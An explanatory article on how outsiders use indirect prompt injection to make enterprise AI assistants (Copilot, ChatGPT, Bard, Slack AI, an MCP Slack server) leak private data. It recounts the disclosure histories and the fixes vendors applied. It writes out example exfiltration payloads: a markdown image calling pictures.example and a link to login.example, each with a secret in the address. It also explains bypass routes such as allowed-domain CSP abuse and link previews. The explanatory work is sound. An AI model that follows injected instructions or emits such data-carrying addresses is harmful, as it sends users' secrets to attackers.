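# Zero-click data exfiltration from enterprise AI assistants

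## What it means for an assistant to leak data without a click

An enterprise AI assistant is a chatbot with access to a company's mail, chats, calendars and files, so that employees can ask questions about those records in ordinary language. Microsoft 365 Copilot is one example, and Slack, Google and Salesforce sell others. Since 2023, security researchers have repeatedly shown that an outsider can put instructions in something the assistant reads, such as an email, and make it send private data to a server the outsider controls. Exfiltration is the security term for moving data out of an organisation to someone not entitled to it. An attack is zero-click if it needs no action from the victim beyond ordinary use of the assistant, so the victim doesn't have to open the malicious item or click anything.

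These attacks work through features that companies pay for, such as search across a whole mailbox and a chat window that can show pictures. They don't require a stolen password or malware on the victim's computer.

### One question, from the prompt to the screen

Suppose an employee asks, "When does our contract with the packaging supplier end?" The assistant's language model wasn't trained on the contract, so other software has to find it first. Fetching relevant documents and giving them to the model with the question is called retrieval-augmented generation, or RAG.

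Microsoft's architecture documentation describes how Copilot answers an employee's prompt. Copilot first looks for related material through Microsoft Graph, the service that gives programs access to an organisation's Microsoft 365 data. It adds what it finds to the prompt and sends the enlarged prompt to the model. It then passes the model's answer back to the employee's app.

Many retrieval systems search by meaning. An encoder turns each passage into a list of numbers, giving similar lists to passages about similar things, and the search returns the passages whose numbers are closest to the question's. Copilot also draws on a "semantic index", according to Microsoft's security documentation. Because this kind of search selects passages by their resemblance to the question, a question about packaging contracts can bring up a stranger's email on the subject.

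Copilot can reach only what the signed-in employee could open by hand. According to the same Microsoft documentation, its searches are "security trimmed", and an attacker who takes over the assistant is confined to that one user's data. A junior clerk's assistant cannot leak the board's papers unless somebody has shared them too widely. Still, one person's access often covers years of mail and many shared folders. The permission check also considers only who may read an item, not who wrote it, so mail from strangers passes because the employee is allowed to read it.

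The assistant then puts everything into the context, which is all the text the model has available when it writes an answer. Itay Ravia (2025) explains in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* that Copilot's context can hold the chat history, items Copilot has fetched from the mailbox, file stores and Teams chats, and details loaded in advance, such as the names of the user and the organisation. It also includes the vendor's standing instructions to the model. In the example, the context might hold the question, the contract, two emails from the supplier and one email from a sender unknown to anyone at the company.

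In the last step, the chat window displays the model's plain-text output as a formatted web page. A simple notation in the text, called markdown, marks what should become a heading, a link or a picture.

### Why a stranger's email can give orders

In indirect prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in content that an assistant reads, and the assistant follows them as if its user had given them. The word "indirect" distinguishes this from cases where the user is the attacker.

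*Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) was an early description of the problem. It noted that previous work on hostile prompts had assumed that the attacker was the user. Once an application retrieves documents, anyone who can put text in those documents can prompt the model. An attacker can place the text on a web page that a search may retrieve, email it directly, or trick users into pasting it themselves. The text can also be hidden from human readers. The group demonstrated attacks on Microsoft's Bing chatbot, which then ran on GPT-4, and on test applications of their own. The paper also described a possible automated attack in which a personal assistant reads an email containing instructions, gathers private data and emails it out. It listed Microsoft 365 Copilot among newly announced products.

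A comparison with SQL injection helps explain why the model does not simply ignore the stranger. In that older flaw, an attacker types database commands into a web form and a careless program runs them. Programmers prevent this by sending the command and the form's contents to the database separately, so the database never treats the contents as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post, David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that no such fix exists for language models. A model receives one sequence of tokens (words and pieces of words) and predicts the next one, with no internal division between commands and contents. In the post's example, a recruiter uses an assistant to score CVs, and a candidate hides a line of text in the CV telling the assistant to approve it.

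Developers label each part of the context with its source (system, user, tool output) and train the model to give some labels more authority than others. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested whether several models internally follow these labels. They trained a small classifier, called a role probe, on the models' internal activity while the models processed identical passages under different labels, so that the probe could learn only from the label. They then gave the models text whose style and label disagreed, and in one model the probe's reading followed the style more than the label. It rated text written like a user's message but labelled as tool output as 88 percent user and 9 percent tool output. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent give up data, the success rate rose from 2 percent where the probe found the least confusion to 70 percent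 where it found the most.

Models can resist simple injected commands. When Ye and colleagues hid plain commands in a web page, most of the 2025 OpenAI models they tested complied at most 2 percent of the time. An attack designed to exploit role confusion raised that figure to between 56 and 70 percent, so this resistance is a weak security barrier against a determined attacker. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities (2026)* similarly describes delimiters, labels and written warnings as useful practice but not a hard boundary. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem (2026)* lists the separation of instructions from data as an open research problem, "if attainable", and adds that even a clean separation would leave gaps, because false data can mislead an agent that ignores any instructions in it.

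### How a picture carries data out

An injected instruction can make the model collect a secret, but the attacker also needs an exfiltration channel, a feature that can send the data out of the organization. The channel may be a link, a tool call or executed code, and in many early cases it was an image.

A web page usually contains the addresses of its pictures rather than the pictures themselves, and the browser automatically requests each picture from the server named in its address as the page loads. Anything after a question mark in an address is extra information for the server, such as a search term or page number. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that servers commonly log the full address of every request. Anyone who can choose the text of an address can therefore use it to send a message to the server's owner.

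Here is the whole sequence with an invented secret. An employee's mailbox holds a note from the facilities team giving the door code of a storeroom, HERON-4471. It also holds an email from a stranger with instructions buried in it. The employee asks the assistant for a summary of the week's mail, and both messages land in the context. The model writes the summary and, following the stranger's instructions, ends it with this line:

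`![logo](https://pictures.example/logo.png?note=HERON-4471)`

This is a markdown image, a line of text that a chat window turns into a picture by requesting a web address. The exclamation mark signals a picture, "logo" is a caption for readers who cannot see it, and the rest is the address. (Standards bodies reserve the ending ".example" for illustrations, so no real website uses it.) When the chat window converts the line, the browser requests a file named logo.png from pictures.example, with the note attached. The stranger, who runs pictures.example, then reads the door code in the server's log.

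The attacker receives the code whether or not an image comes back, because the request itself contains the code. Encrypting the connection does not help either, since encryption protects the request from eavesdroppers and the attacker is the intended recipient. The employee sees a normal summary, perhaps with a small broken-image icon below it.

A Content Security Policy (CSP), a browser defence that predates chatbots, lists the domains from which a web page may load images and other resources. The site sends the list with the page, and the browser enforces it. If the assistant's page allows images only from the vendor's own domains, the browser never sends the request that would carry the door code to pictures.example. According to the *Bing Chat* post on the security blog Embrace The Red, a policy of this kind was at least part of Microsoft's fix for an image leak in 2023.

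A CSP's protection depends on which domains it allows. Large products need pictures from many places, so their lists grow long. Some of the listed servers also offer a proxy fetch, in which the server requests another address on a user's behalf. A chat service, for example, may use one to retrieve a linked article and show a preview. Suppose the model writes an image address that points to such a server and tells it to fetch `pictures.example/logo.png?note=HERON-4471`. The browser finds the server's domain on the list and allows the request. The trusted server then contacts pictures.example itself, which the CSP can't prevent because it restricts only the browser. A flaw that lets an attacker choose the address a server fetches is called server-side request forgery. In one 2026 attack on Copilot, according to the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, the trusted server belonged to Microsoft's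 search engine, Bing.

### The lethal trifecta

The door-code theft needed a secret the assistant could read, a stranger's text in the same context, and a route to the stranger's server. The programmer Simon Willison (2025) named this combination in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, listing its parts as access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection" in 2022, was writing mainly for people who connect their own tools to a model and may combine all three without noticing.

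The theft requires access to private data, exposure to text from outside, and a way to send data out, so removing any one of these stops it. In the storeroom example, if the assistant cannot read the mailbox, the stranger's instructions may still run, but the assistant has no access to the door code. If it reads the mailbox but never sees text from outside, it never receives the instruction to put the code in an address. If the browser makes no outside requests and no other channel exists, the model can still write the line containing the code, but the line stays on the employee's screen. The injection has succeeded in that last case, and the stranger can still use it to spoil the summary or mislead the employee, but gets no data.

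A vendor of a workplace assistant has little choice about which of the three to remove. The product exists to read private data, and an assistant that ignored all outside mail would be of little use to anyone who deals with customers. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* (2026) therefore treats Copilot as having these two by default, and external communication as the only one a vendor can realistically enforce limits on. Willison, in a September 2025 note, also calls external communication generally the easiest to remove. Google has taken this approach with images by not letting its Gemini assistant render them from external addresses.

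Removal has to be complete, however, and this is difficult. Willison describes the ways a tool might pass data out as "almost limitless", since any web request will do. If a vendor blocks images but leaves another kind of request open, an attacker can use that instead. Filters that try to spot malicious incoming text only lower the odds of a successful attack, since an attacker can keep rewording the email until one version gets through.

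### What the victim has to do

A "zero-click" attack requires no mistake by the victim, such as opening a suspicious attachment. With workplace assistants, though, somebody usually still has to ask the assistant a question for which the search brings up the attacker's email. SC Media's report on GeminiJack, an attack on Google's assistant, repeats the discoverers' label "zero-click" and explains that the attack starts when the target runs a routine search. Employers buy these assistants so that staff can ask them about work, so training staff to be careful does little against this sort of attack.

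A one-click attack needs the victim to click one link. Sometimes the link is in the assistant's answer, with the secret already in its address. Clicking it sends the secret to the attacker, which in a zero-click attack the browser can do automatically by loading an image. The 2024 attack on Slack AI, the assistant built into the workplace chat service Slack, worked this way, though people often mention it alongside zero-click attacks. Other one-click attacks start when the victim clicks a link that opens the assistant with the attacker's question already filled in.

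In other cases the user directs the assistant to the malicious item, by asking it to summarise a particular web page or by opening a shared document and starting a chat inside it. Ravia uses this difference to distinguish EchoLeak, the 2025 email attack on Copilot, from earlier demonstrations. Researchers disagree about whether such cases count as zero-click. In one demonstration from Embrace The Red's talk, a user opens a booby-trapped Word file and types only "hi there" to Copilot. Embrace The Red counts this as zero-click because the user only used Copilot normally. The stricter definition used here excludes it because the user opened the malicious file.

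The software around an assistant can also determine whether the same attack needs a click. Messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram request a link's address to build a preview of it. PromptArmor, a security firm, warns that when an AI agent's reply appears in such an app, the preview immediately sends the same kind of request as a click would. This removes the one click that the leak needed in a browser window.

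## 2023: chat answers that sent data out through images

In spring 2023, two people independently discovered that ChatGPT could send a conversation to a stranger through the address of an image. Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found the leak at the end of March, and Johann Rehberger, the security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, found it in early April. Rehberger reported the flaw to Microsoft, whose Bing Chat also had it, on 8 April and to OpenAI on 9 April. In September, he and two collaborators reported a third case, in the chatbot Bard, to Google.

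All three were consumer chatbots. In the Bing Chat and ChatGPT cases, an attacker could get at most the conversation and the web page the user was reading. Bard had just gained access to its users' mail and documents, which made it the closest of the three to a workplace assistant.

### Bing Chat and the hostile comment

Bing Chat could answer questions about the web page a user had open. To do so, it put the page's text into the model's context, including text the page's owner hadn't written, such as a reader's comment or an advertisement. Rehberger placed instructions in a web page. In the test Embrace The Red describes, the instructions took effect as soon as the user opened the page and began chatting, but the image didn't appear until two exchanges later. Rehberger had built in the delay to show that the author of the hidden text controlled the chatbot for the rest of the conversation.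 The image's address contained a short encoded summary of the page and the chat, along with a secret from further down the page.

Suppose a shop's website shows a customer's account details above other people's product reviews. By Rehberger's reasoning, an attacker could steal those details with one hostile review if the customer opened Bing Chat on that page. The victim didn't have to click the image, but did have to visit the page and start a conversation there, so the attack was not strictly zero-click.

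Microsoft acknowledged the problem and told Rehberger on 15 June 2023, 68 days after the report, that it had put a fix in place. The old tests no longer worked, and Rehberger found that Bing Chat's page now had a Content Security Policy that allowed images from only four Bing domains, which the chatbot still needed to show pictures it had created. Rehberger was examining the fix from outside Microsoft and noted that the company might have made other changes too. A later post, Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, dates the policy to May 2023, so it may have been in place for some weeks before Microsoft told Rehberger about the fix.

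The policy stopped the leak, but a comment on a web page could still inject instructions that changed the chatbot's answers. Rehberger also suspected that Microsoft had blocked the domain used in the tests, which would have stopped the demonstrations but not an attacker with a different domain.

### ChatGPT: "a feature"

The first published version of the ChatGPT leak worked only if the user pasted copied text without rereading it. In *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, Samoilenko describes a website with a script that adds instructions to any text a visitor copies. When the visitor pastes the text into ChatGPT, the answer includes a transparent, one-pixel-wide image with data from the chat in its address. The instructions could also make ChatGPT include the image in every later answer, which would send each new question to the attacker's server.

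Samoilenko reported that ChatGPT's output varied between attempts, so an attack that worked once could fail the next time. The user's earlier prompts or a piece of code were easy to extract, but passwords and access keys were very difficult. Samoilenko accepted that users are responsible for checking what they paste, but thought OpenAI should stop ChatGPT from putting markdown images in its replies. Willison (2023) drew attention to the finding on 14 April in a note with the same title.

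Plugins made the pasting unnecessary. These add-ons, mostly from other companies, let ChatGPT do things such as fetch a web page or a video's transcript. In the 2023 post *ChatGPT Plugins*, Rehberger had ChatGPT read a web page through the WebPilot plugin. Instructions on the page told the model to summarise the earlier conversation and put the summary in an image address. The text that reached Rehberger's server included a password-like string that the user had typed earlier in the chat. Another test page made ChatGPT search for flights through a second plugin, from the travel company Expedia.

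Rehberger questioned why plugin content should share a context with the whole conversation. A tool that fetches one page doesn't need access to the earlier conversation, and keeping the two separate would have left little data for an attacker to steal through instructions on the page.

OpenAI had no bug bounty programme (a scheme that pays outsiders for reporting flaws) when Rehberger reported the leak, so they discussed it by email. Rehberger pointed out that plugins would let attackers exploit it remotely. By Rehberger's account, OpenAI answered that image markdown injection was a feature and that the company planned no changes. Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*, published later that year, lists the report as "won't fix".

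OpenAI's answer had some merit. ChatGPT was displaying images as its developers intended, and Samoilenko had described the attack as a combination of tricks that exploited no vulnerability. But Microsoft received a report of the same behaviour in the same week and treated it as a security flaw. OpenAI's argument also weakened as the company added features that brought strangers' text into the chat.

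In September Rehberger found a way around another limit, the small amount of text that fits comfortably in a web address. Some plugins could create documents, diagrams or videos and store them online. Injected instructions could make one of these plugins save the whole conversation, so the image address only had to contain a link to the saved copy. Rehberger sent OpenAI a draft of this work on 23 September and received only an automated response.

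Two months later, OpenAI let paying users build GPTs, versions of ChatGPT with their own standing instructions. Embrace The Red's *Malicious ChatGPT Agents* describes one that offered to play tic-tac-toe but first asked for personal information, including an email address and password. It sent whatever the user typed to Rehberger's server through hidden images. This attack needed no indirect injection because the attacker had written the chatbot's instructions. OpenAI's automated screening rejected a first version of the GPT but let a reworded one through. Rehberger reported it on 13 November, and OpenAI closed the report two days later as "Not Applicable". He published the findings after two follow-up messages went unanswered. SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server* gives the publication date as 12 December.

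### The address check, and the apps without it

OpenAI added protection to the web version of ChatGPT shortly afterwards, more than eight months after the first report. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* records that ChatGPT was still leaking data during a live demonstration the day before.

OpenAI had added a check called url_safe. Before requesting an image in an answer, the ChatGPT page in the user's browser sent the image's address to an OpenAI server, and it requested the image only if the server classified the address as safe. The server classified the address of Rehberger's server, with an email address attached, as unsafe.

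OpenAI did not publish the rules for which images the check allowed. Rehberger saw that images from unfamiliar websites still sometimes appeared, and tested 36 image addresses, each standing for one letter or digit. The check allowed 9 of them. This would have leaked only tiny amounts of data, slowly, and OpenAI could have noticed the series of requests in its logs. Rehberger could not find a reason why the check allowed one image and blocked another from the same folder on the same server.

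In *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, Willison (2023) called OpenAI's solution "half-baked" and thought it odd that the company hadn't simply blocked images from external domains. Willison expected a suitably creative attacker to get past the check. Rehberger and the security firm Tenable (2025) had each found ways to do so by the end of 2024.

A more basic weakness was that the check worked only in apps that included it. The server could tell an app whether an image was safe, but it did not remove unsafe images from the answer. The iPhone app didn't include the check, so the original attack still worked there. The Android app had the same gap, as did the macOS app that OpenAI released in 2024. Rehberger had suggested doing the check on the server, where it would protect every app, and guessed that OpenAI had avoided this so that answers could appear word by word.

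By then the leak could do more harm because OpenAI had given ChatGPT a long-term memory. The model could save notes about a user, which the software added to the context of later conversations. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* shows how an attacker could combine this memory with the missing check in the macOS app. When a user asked ChatGPT to look at a hostile website, instructions on the site made the model save a note with an instruction to attach an image with chat data to its answers. The user's messages and ChatGPT's replies then went to the attacker's server, including those in new conversations unrelated to the website.

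In May 2024, Rehberger reported that websites could plant false memories in ChatGPT. OpenAI closed the report, classifying the problem as a model safety issue rather than a security issue. In June, Rehberger demonstrated the full data theft. OpenAI fixed the macOS app in September 2024, 17 months after the image leak was first reported. The fix stopped images from carrying data out, but websites could still write to ChatGPT's memory.

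OpenAI has since changed the rule behind the check, with a major revision around August 2025, and explained the current version in January 2026. A crawler with no access to users' conversations records addresses that are already public on the web. ChatGPT can load an address automatically if the crawler has recorded exactly that address. Otherwise, ChatGPT has to try a different site, or the user sees a warning and decides whether to continue. An address containing the storeroom code HERON-4471 would fail the check, because nobody would have published it before the model composed it. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* calls the mechanism Safe Url and says it also applies to page visits in the company's Atlas browser and its Deep Research tool.

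This rule is much stricter than the one Rehberger tested in 2023, although small leaks remain possible. If a model can choose between two public pages on an attacker's website, the attacker can learn something from its choice. Rehberger also pointed out that a developer at OpenAI might not know about the check and could build a new product without it, a risk the missing apps had already illustrated.

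### Google Bard and the shared document

On 19 September 2023 Google launched Bard Extensions, which let its chatbot look things up in a user's Gmail, Docs and Drive, and in services such as YouTube and Google Maps. *Bard can now connect to your Google apps and services* (Pinsky, 2023) gave the example of planning a trip by having Bard find dates in Gmail that suited everyone. On the day of the launch, Rehberger, Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake, lead author of the 2023 paper on indirect prompt injection, reported a working attack to Google.

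The instructions came in a Google Doc. Anyone can share a document with another Google user without that user's consent, so an attacker could put text within Bard's reach. Rehberger worried that the victim might then search for something with Bard and bring up the attacker's document. In the demonstration, the user simply chatted with Bard and then brought the shared document into the conversation. Bard followed the document's instructions and added an image whose address contained the first 20 words of the chat.

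The demonstration took text from the conversation and did not show mail leaving the account. But any email text Bard had already quoted to the user would have been in the conversation too. In *Hacking Google Bard*, Willison described the attack as the first reported prompt injection against the extended Bard.

Bard already had the protection that Microsoft had added to Bing Chat. Google's Content Security Policy at first stopped the browser from requesting an image from the researchers' own server. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* explains that they got around this with Google Apps Script, which lets the public run small programs at addresses under google.com and googleusercontent.com. The policy allowed images from any address under those two domains.

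People normally use Apps Script to automate work in Google's office programs, much as they use macros in Microsoft Office. They can also publish a script as a web app with its own address. According to Google's documentation, when someone requests that address, the script receives any extra information attached to it. Rehberger wrote a script that accepted requests from anyone and copied this information into a Google Doc.

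Once the script was in place, Bard wrote an image address that pointed to it, with words from the conversation attached. The policy allowed addresses under google.com, so the browser made the request. The script ran on Google's servers and saved the words in a Google Doc that the attacker could read. The data had left the victim's account without having to go to a server outside Google. The demonstration came less than 24 hours after the launch of Extensions, according to Singh's *How a Prompt Injection Vulnerability Led to Data Exfiltration*, an article for the bug bounty company HackerOne.

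On 19 October, a month after the report, Rehberger asked Google about its progress because of an upcoming conference talk. Google confirmed that it had fixed the flaw but did not say how, and Rehberger could not tell from outside. The policy was the same as before, and Bard still displayed images. Rehberger's best guess was that Google now filtered Bard's output to keep data out of image addresses. If so, Apps Script was still an allowed destination, and the protection depended on the filter recognising each attempt.

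### Why allowing a domain means trusting everything on it

The Bard policy worked as written. A domain in a CSP identifies who runs the server that receives a request, but not who wrote the code that handles it. For a small company's website, the two are usually the same. Google, however, hosts search, private documents, public forms and users' scripts under one domain, so a browser enforcing the policy cannot distinguish Google's own code from a script published by an attacker.

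An attacker can therefore get data out through an allowed domain if any service on it stores what it receives and lets an outsider read it later. The company may also add such a service after a developer has approved the domain, so the list can become less safe without anyone editing it.

Google's own researchers had documented the general problem years earlier. *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues, 2016) studied policies collected from a search engine's copy of about 100 billion web pages and found ways around 94.72 percent of the distinct policies. According to the conference abstract of *We Broke All CSPs and You Won't Believe What Happened Next*, a later HITB talk on the same work, 75.81 percent of the policies could be bypassed because of their lists of allowed domains alone.

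Those figures cover CSP's use against hostile scripts, so they don't measure how many chatbots would leak data through images. But an allowed domain is arguably easier to exploit for an image leak, because the attacker only needs a place on it that records requests, rather than code that can be used to run a hostile script. The Google researchers recommended marking approved scripts with one-time tokens instead of listing allowed domains, but CSP has no equivalent for images.

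OpenAI gives another reason for not relying on lists of trusted sites. Many legitimate websites forward visitors to other addresses, so a request can start at a trusted domain and end at the attacker's. A check of only the first address would miss this. Short lists also trigger warnings about harmless sites, and OpenAI worries that users learn to click through the warnings.

In January 2026, Willison noted the same mistake in the email app Superhuman, where the policy allowed images from docs.google.com. Google Forms, which runs on that domain, accepted the stolen data and stored it for the attacker.

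### A policy, a check or no images

Anyone could inspect Microsoft's fix, so Rehberger could read the four allowed domains and judge the remaining risk. The browser also applies the policy to every image on the page, whichever part of the software put it there. The four named Bing domains gave an attacker far fewer services to search through than Bard's two open-ended entries, but Microsoft still had to trust those four servers to handle requests safely.

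OpenAI's check can distinguish between two addresses on the same domain. In its current form, it would block a newly composed address at script.google.com but still load a well-known picture from another Google site. This lets ChatGPT show images from across the web, which a short list of allowed domains would prevent. It also gives OpenAI a central record of suspicious addresses. However, users and outside researchers have to trust rules they can't fully inspect, and every app has to call the check.

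Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* reports that Generative AI Studio, a tool for developers in Google's cloud service, leaked chat data through images until Google stopped it from displaying images and links altogether. Rehberger considered this probably the best possible fix for security. Unlike a CSP for images, it also blocked links that send data when a user clicks them. A tool for testing prompts loses little without images, but Microsoft could not have removed them so easily from Bing Chat, which created images for its users.

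Google had accepted the Vertex AI report on 30 August 2023, 22 minutes after Rehberger submitted it and 20 days before the launch of Bard Extensions. Other Google products also had the flaw. NotebookLM, Google's tool for questioning a collection of documents, was still leaking data 132 days after Rehberger reported it, according to Embrace The Red's *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps* (2024). Google deployed a fix in April 2024, after the post appeared. In August 2024, Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio* showed how one malicious file in a batch of staff performance reviews could make AI Studio send summaries of all the others to an outside server, through images that no CSP restricted.

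Google's security team had given no date for fixing AI Studio. Rehberger then raised the issue publicly with a Google employee on X, and within 24 hours AI Studio was displaying the image code as plain text.

The image leak also recurred in Microsoft's products. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground* describes a variant in the company's cloud tools after the Bing Chat fix. *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) lists 11 products in which Rehberger had found and reported the leak by December 2024. Five were Google's and three were Microsoft's, including GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant for programmers.

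## 2024: Slack AI and an early attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot

In August 2024, researchers published attacks on two workplace assistants. PromptArmor described a leak in Slack AI on 20 August, and Rehberger described one in Microsoft 365 Copilot on 24 August. Both assistants could search an organisation's internal records, so an attacker could steal much more than the chat transcripts at risk in 2023. Both attacks placed the data in a link, which the victim had to click to send it to the attacker.

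### A key in a private channel

Every member of a company's Slack workspace can find and read its public channels, while a private channel is open only to the people in it. Slack AI answered questions by retrieving messages from any channel the user could read, including public channels they had never joined.

PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* describes the theft of an API key, a secret string that a program uses to identify itself to an online service. A developer saves the key in a private channel with no other members. The attacker has an account in the same workspace but can't see that channel, so they create a public channel and post one message there. The message names the service, so a search for that service's key is likely to retrieve the message. It also tells the model to answer with an error notice and a link, and to replace a placeholder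 word in the link's address with the key.

Later the developer asks Slack AI for the key. Slack AI retrieves the private note and the attacker's message and puts both in the context. The model follows the attacker's message, so the developer sees an error notice with an invitation to "click here to reauthenticate". With an invented key and a placeholder address, the link would lead here:

`https://login.example/renew?key=PLOVER-2093`

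The developer can see the address only by hovering over the link. Clicking it sends the key to the attacker. Someone who has just asked for a login secret may well not be suspicious of a request to log in again.

Slack AI normally cites the messages behind an answer, but in this demonstration it cited only the developer's private channel, not the attacker's message. That message didn't appear on the first page of search results either, so PromptArmor considered the attack very difficult to trace.

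PromptArmor also showed a simpler attack. The victim asks for a summary of a manager's messages and receives a link to a phishing page (a fake page used to steal a password or other secret). This time Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel, and PromptArmor concluded that the citations were fairly random.

Willison (2024) stressed in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection* that the key was only an example. An attacker could use the same method to steal other private details without knowing what they were. PromptArmor's search also returned other messages about API keys, which suggested that an attacker might not have to name a particular secret. But the firm's headline claim, that attackers could steal anything a user put in a private channel, was broader than its demonstration supported, because the victim still had to ask a question that retrieved both the secret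 and the attacker's message, and then click the link.

### "Intended behavior"

PromptArmor reported the flaw to Slack on 14 August. Slack asked for more information the next day, and PromptArmor sent further videos and screenshots and said it planned to publish. After another exchange on 16 August, Slack replied on 19 August that the evidence was insufficient. It wrote that the information the user asked for in the first video was in a public channel, and that letting all members search public channels was "intended behavior".

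PromptArmor published its report the next day, and Slack deployed a patch that same day. In a statement on 21 August, Slack (2024) said that someone with an account in the workspace could, "under very limited and specific circumstances", phish other users for certain data. Slack had no evidence that anyone had gained unauthorised access to customer data. A spokesperson told the technology site ITPro much the same (*Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages*), and described the risk as one user tricking another into sharing data through a crafted link.

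Slack was right that its search was working as designed. Public channels exist so that colleagues can find things in them, and an assistant that ignored every channel its user hadn't joined would miss much of the company's information. But Slack's response didn't address PromptArmor's complaint. No permission check failed, because the developer was entitled to read both the private note and the attacker's message. The leak happened because the model followed instructions in the attacker's message and applied them to the private note.

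Willison took Slack's reply as a sign that the company did not yet understand the nature or severity of the problem. Slack may instead have been misled by a citation. Its reply relied on the source cited in the first video, and a reviewer who saw a public channel cited could have assumed that the secret came from there. PromptArmor had found the citations unreliable. However, Slack had received the additional videos four days before it replied.

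Slack also had some reason to call the circumstances limited. SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing* lists the same conditions: access to the victim's workspace, a public channel and a click. It adds that any colleague could read the posted instructions, which makes discovery more likely, although a channel with one member could go unnoticed until somebody searched for it. These conditions make the attack much harder than sending an email to a stranger, but they offer less protection against an employee with a grudge. PromptArmor pointed to earlier leaks through Slack at companies including Disney and Uber.

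However, "phish" was a poor description of the main attack. An ordinary phishing page gives the victim a chance to become suspicious before typing in a password, but the link in the API key attack already contained the secret, so clicking it was enough to leak the key. Slack's wording fits the demonstration with the manager's messages much better.

PromptArmor published its findings only six days after first reporting them to Slack. It argued that customers needed to know in time to change their settings, because Slack AI had just gained access to more material. That argument is reasonable when a vendor has declined to treat a report as a vulnerability. Slack released a patch on the day of publication, which suggests that the publicity had some effect.

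Slack didn't explain what the patch changed. Its current security documentation lists several guardrails for its AI features, including filtering web addresses to prevent phishing and "context engineering" to reduce the risk of prompt injection. Slack also says there that the AI features use only data the member can already access, and that customer data never leaves infrastructure Slack controls. The first assurance would also have been true during PromptArmor's attack. The second concerns where Slack runs the models, which made no difference in the attack because the developer's own browser sent the key out.

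### From messages to files

On the day PromptArmor sent its report, Slack AI began to use uploaded files as well as messages in its answers. This mattered because an outsider's main obstacle had been needing an account in the workspace.

Suppose an attacker publishes a PDF, perhaps an industry report, with instructions in white text on a white page. If an employee downloads it and uploads it to a Slack channel, Slack AI can retrieve the instructions, even though the attacker has never had a Slack account. The attack could then proceed as before, with a question that retrieves both the file and a secret, and an answer containing a link.

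PromptArmor had finished testing before the change and did not test instructions in files. It said such an attack was highly likely to work, given how Slack AI had treated messages, and advised administrators to restrict the assistant's access to files until Slack fixed the problem. SC Media asked Salesforce, Slack's owner, about instructions in files but got no answer on that point. Slack's statement that the attacker needed an existing account applied to the attack PromptArmor had demonstrated, but it remained unclear whether an outsider could do the same with a file.

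The new feature was on by default, although owners and administrators could restrict it. According to Slack's help page, it covered most file types but not images, spreadsheets or objects embedded in documents, so the exclusions would not have stopped the PDF.

Slack's AI has since gained more sources. Slack's current help page includes previews of shared links, which usually contain a title and description chosen by the linked site's owner. An outsider could in principle get the assistant to read their text by getting an employee to share a link. Slack's *Search across your applications with enterprise search* explains that Slackbot, the company's assistant, also uses content from other applications that a customer connects. These sources make the assistant more useful but also give more people a chance to write something it will read.

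### Link previews that remove the click

When someone posts a link in Slack, a small preview of the page usually appears under the message. To build the preview, a Slack server requests the linked address and reads the page's title, description and picture. This is called link unfurling, and many chat programs do it.

If an AI agent posted the link to login.example as an ordinary Slack message, Slack would send PLOVER-2093 to the attacker while building the preview, without anyone clicking. A Content Security Policy wouldn't stop this, because the preview is a proxy fetch to an address the attacker chose.

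Link previews were a sensible default when only people posted links, since a person who posts a link has generally chosen what to share. But an agent may post a link that an attacker designed to include data the agent has just read from a private file.

Rehberger explained the danger in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, published on Embrace The Red. The day after PromptArmor's report, Willison (2024) admitted in a note with the same title that he had not thought of this route before. Slack unfurls links in messages from apps by default, but a developer can turn this off for each message with two settings, one for ordinary pages and one for media such as images. When Rehberger posted a test link without those settings, the server logged a request from Slack's preview software.

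PromptArmor's attack on Slack AI did not use this route. Slack's documentation describes unfurling for posted messages, whereas an AI search answer disappears when the user closes it. The risk applies to the many other agents that companies allow to post in Slack.

One such connection was a small program from Anthropic, which makes the Claude models. It let an agent read and post Slack messages through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of connecting AI models to tools. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* shows how it leaked data in 2025. In one demonstration, a user asked Claude to summarise a document and post the summary for the team. Instructions in the document made Claude read the latest message in another channel and post a link whose address contained that message. Slack fetched the link to generate a preview, which sent the message to Rehberger's server.

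Claude had posted the link in a private channel. A company that limited the program to that channel could reasonably think an agent posting there unsupervised could not send anything outside, but the link preview made this possible.

Rehberger reported the flaw on 27 May 2025. Anthropic archived the program two days later, though Rehberger could not tell whether his report was the reason. People were still downloading it more than 14,000 times a week, and Anthropic did not plan to patch it. The flaw received a CVE number, which identifies it in the public catalogue of security flaws. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-34072* (2025), the Spanish national cybersecurity institute's entry on the flaw, rates its severity 9.3 out of 10 and calls the result "zero-click exfiltration". The data did leave without a click, but in Rehberger's demonstrations the user had first asked the agent to read the malicious file.

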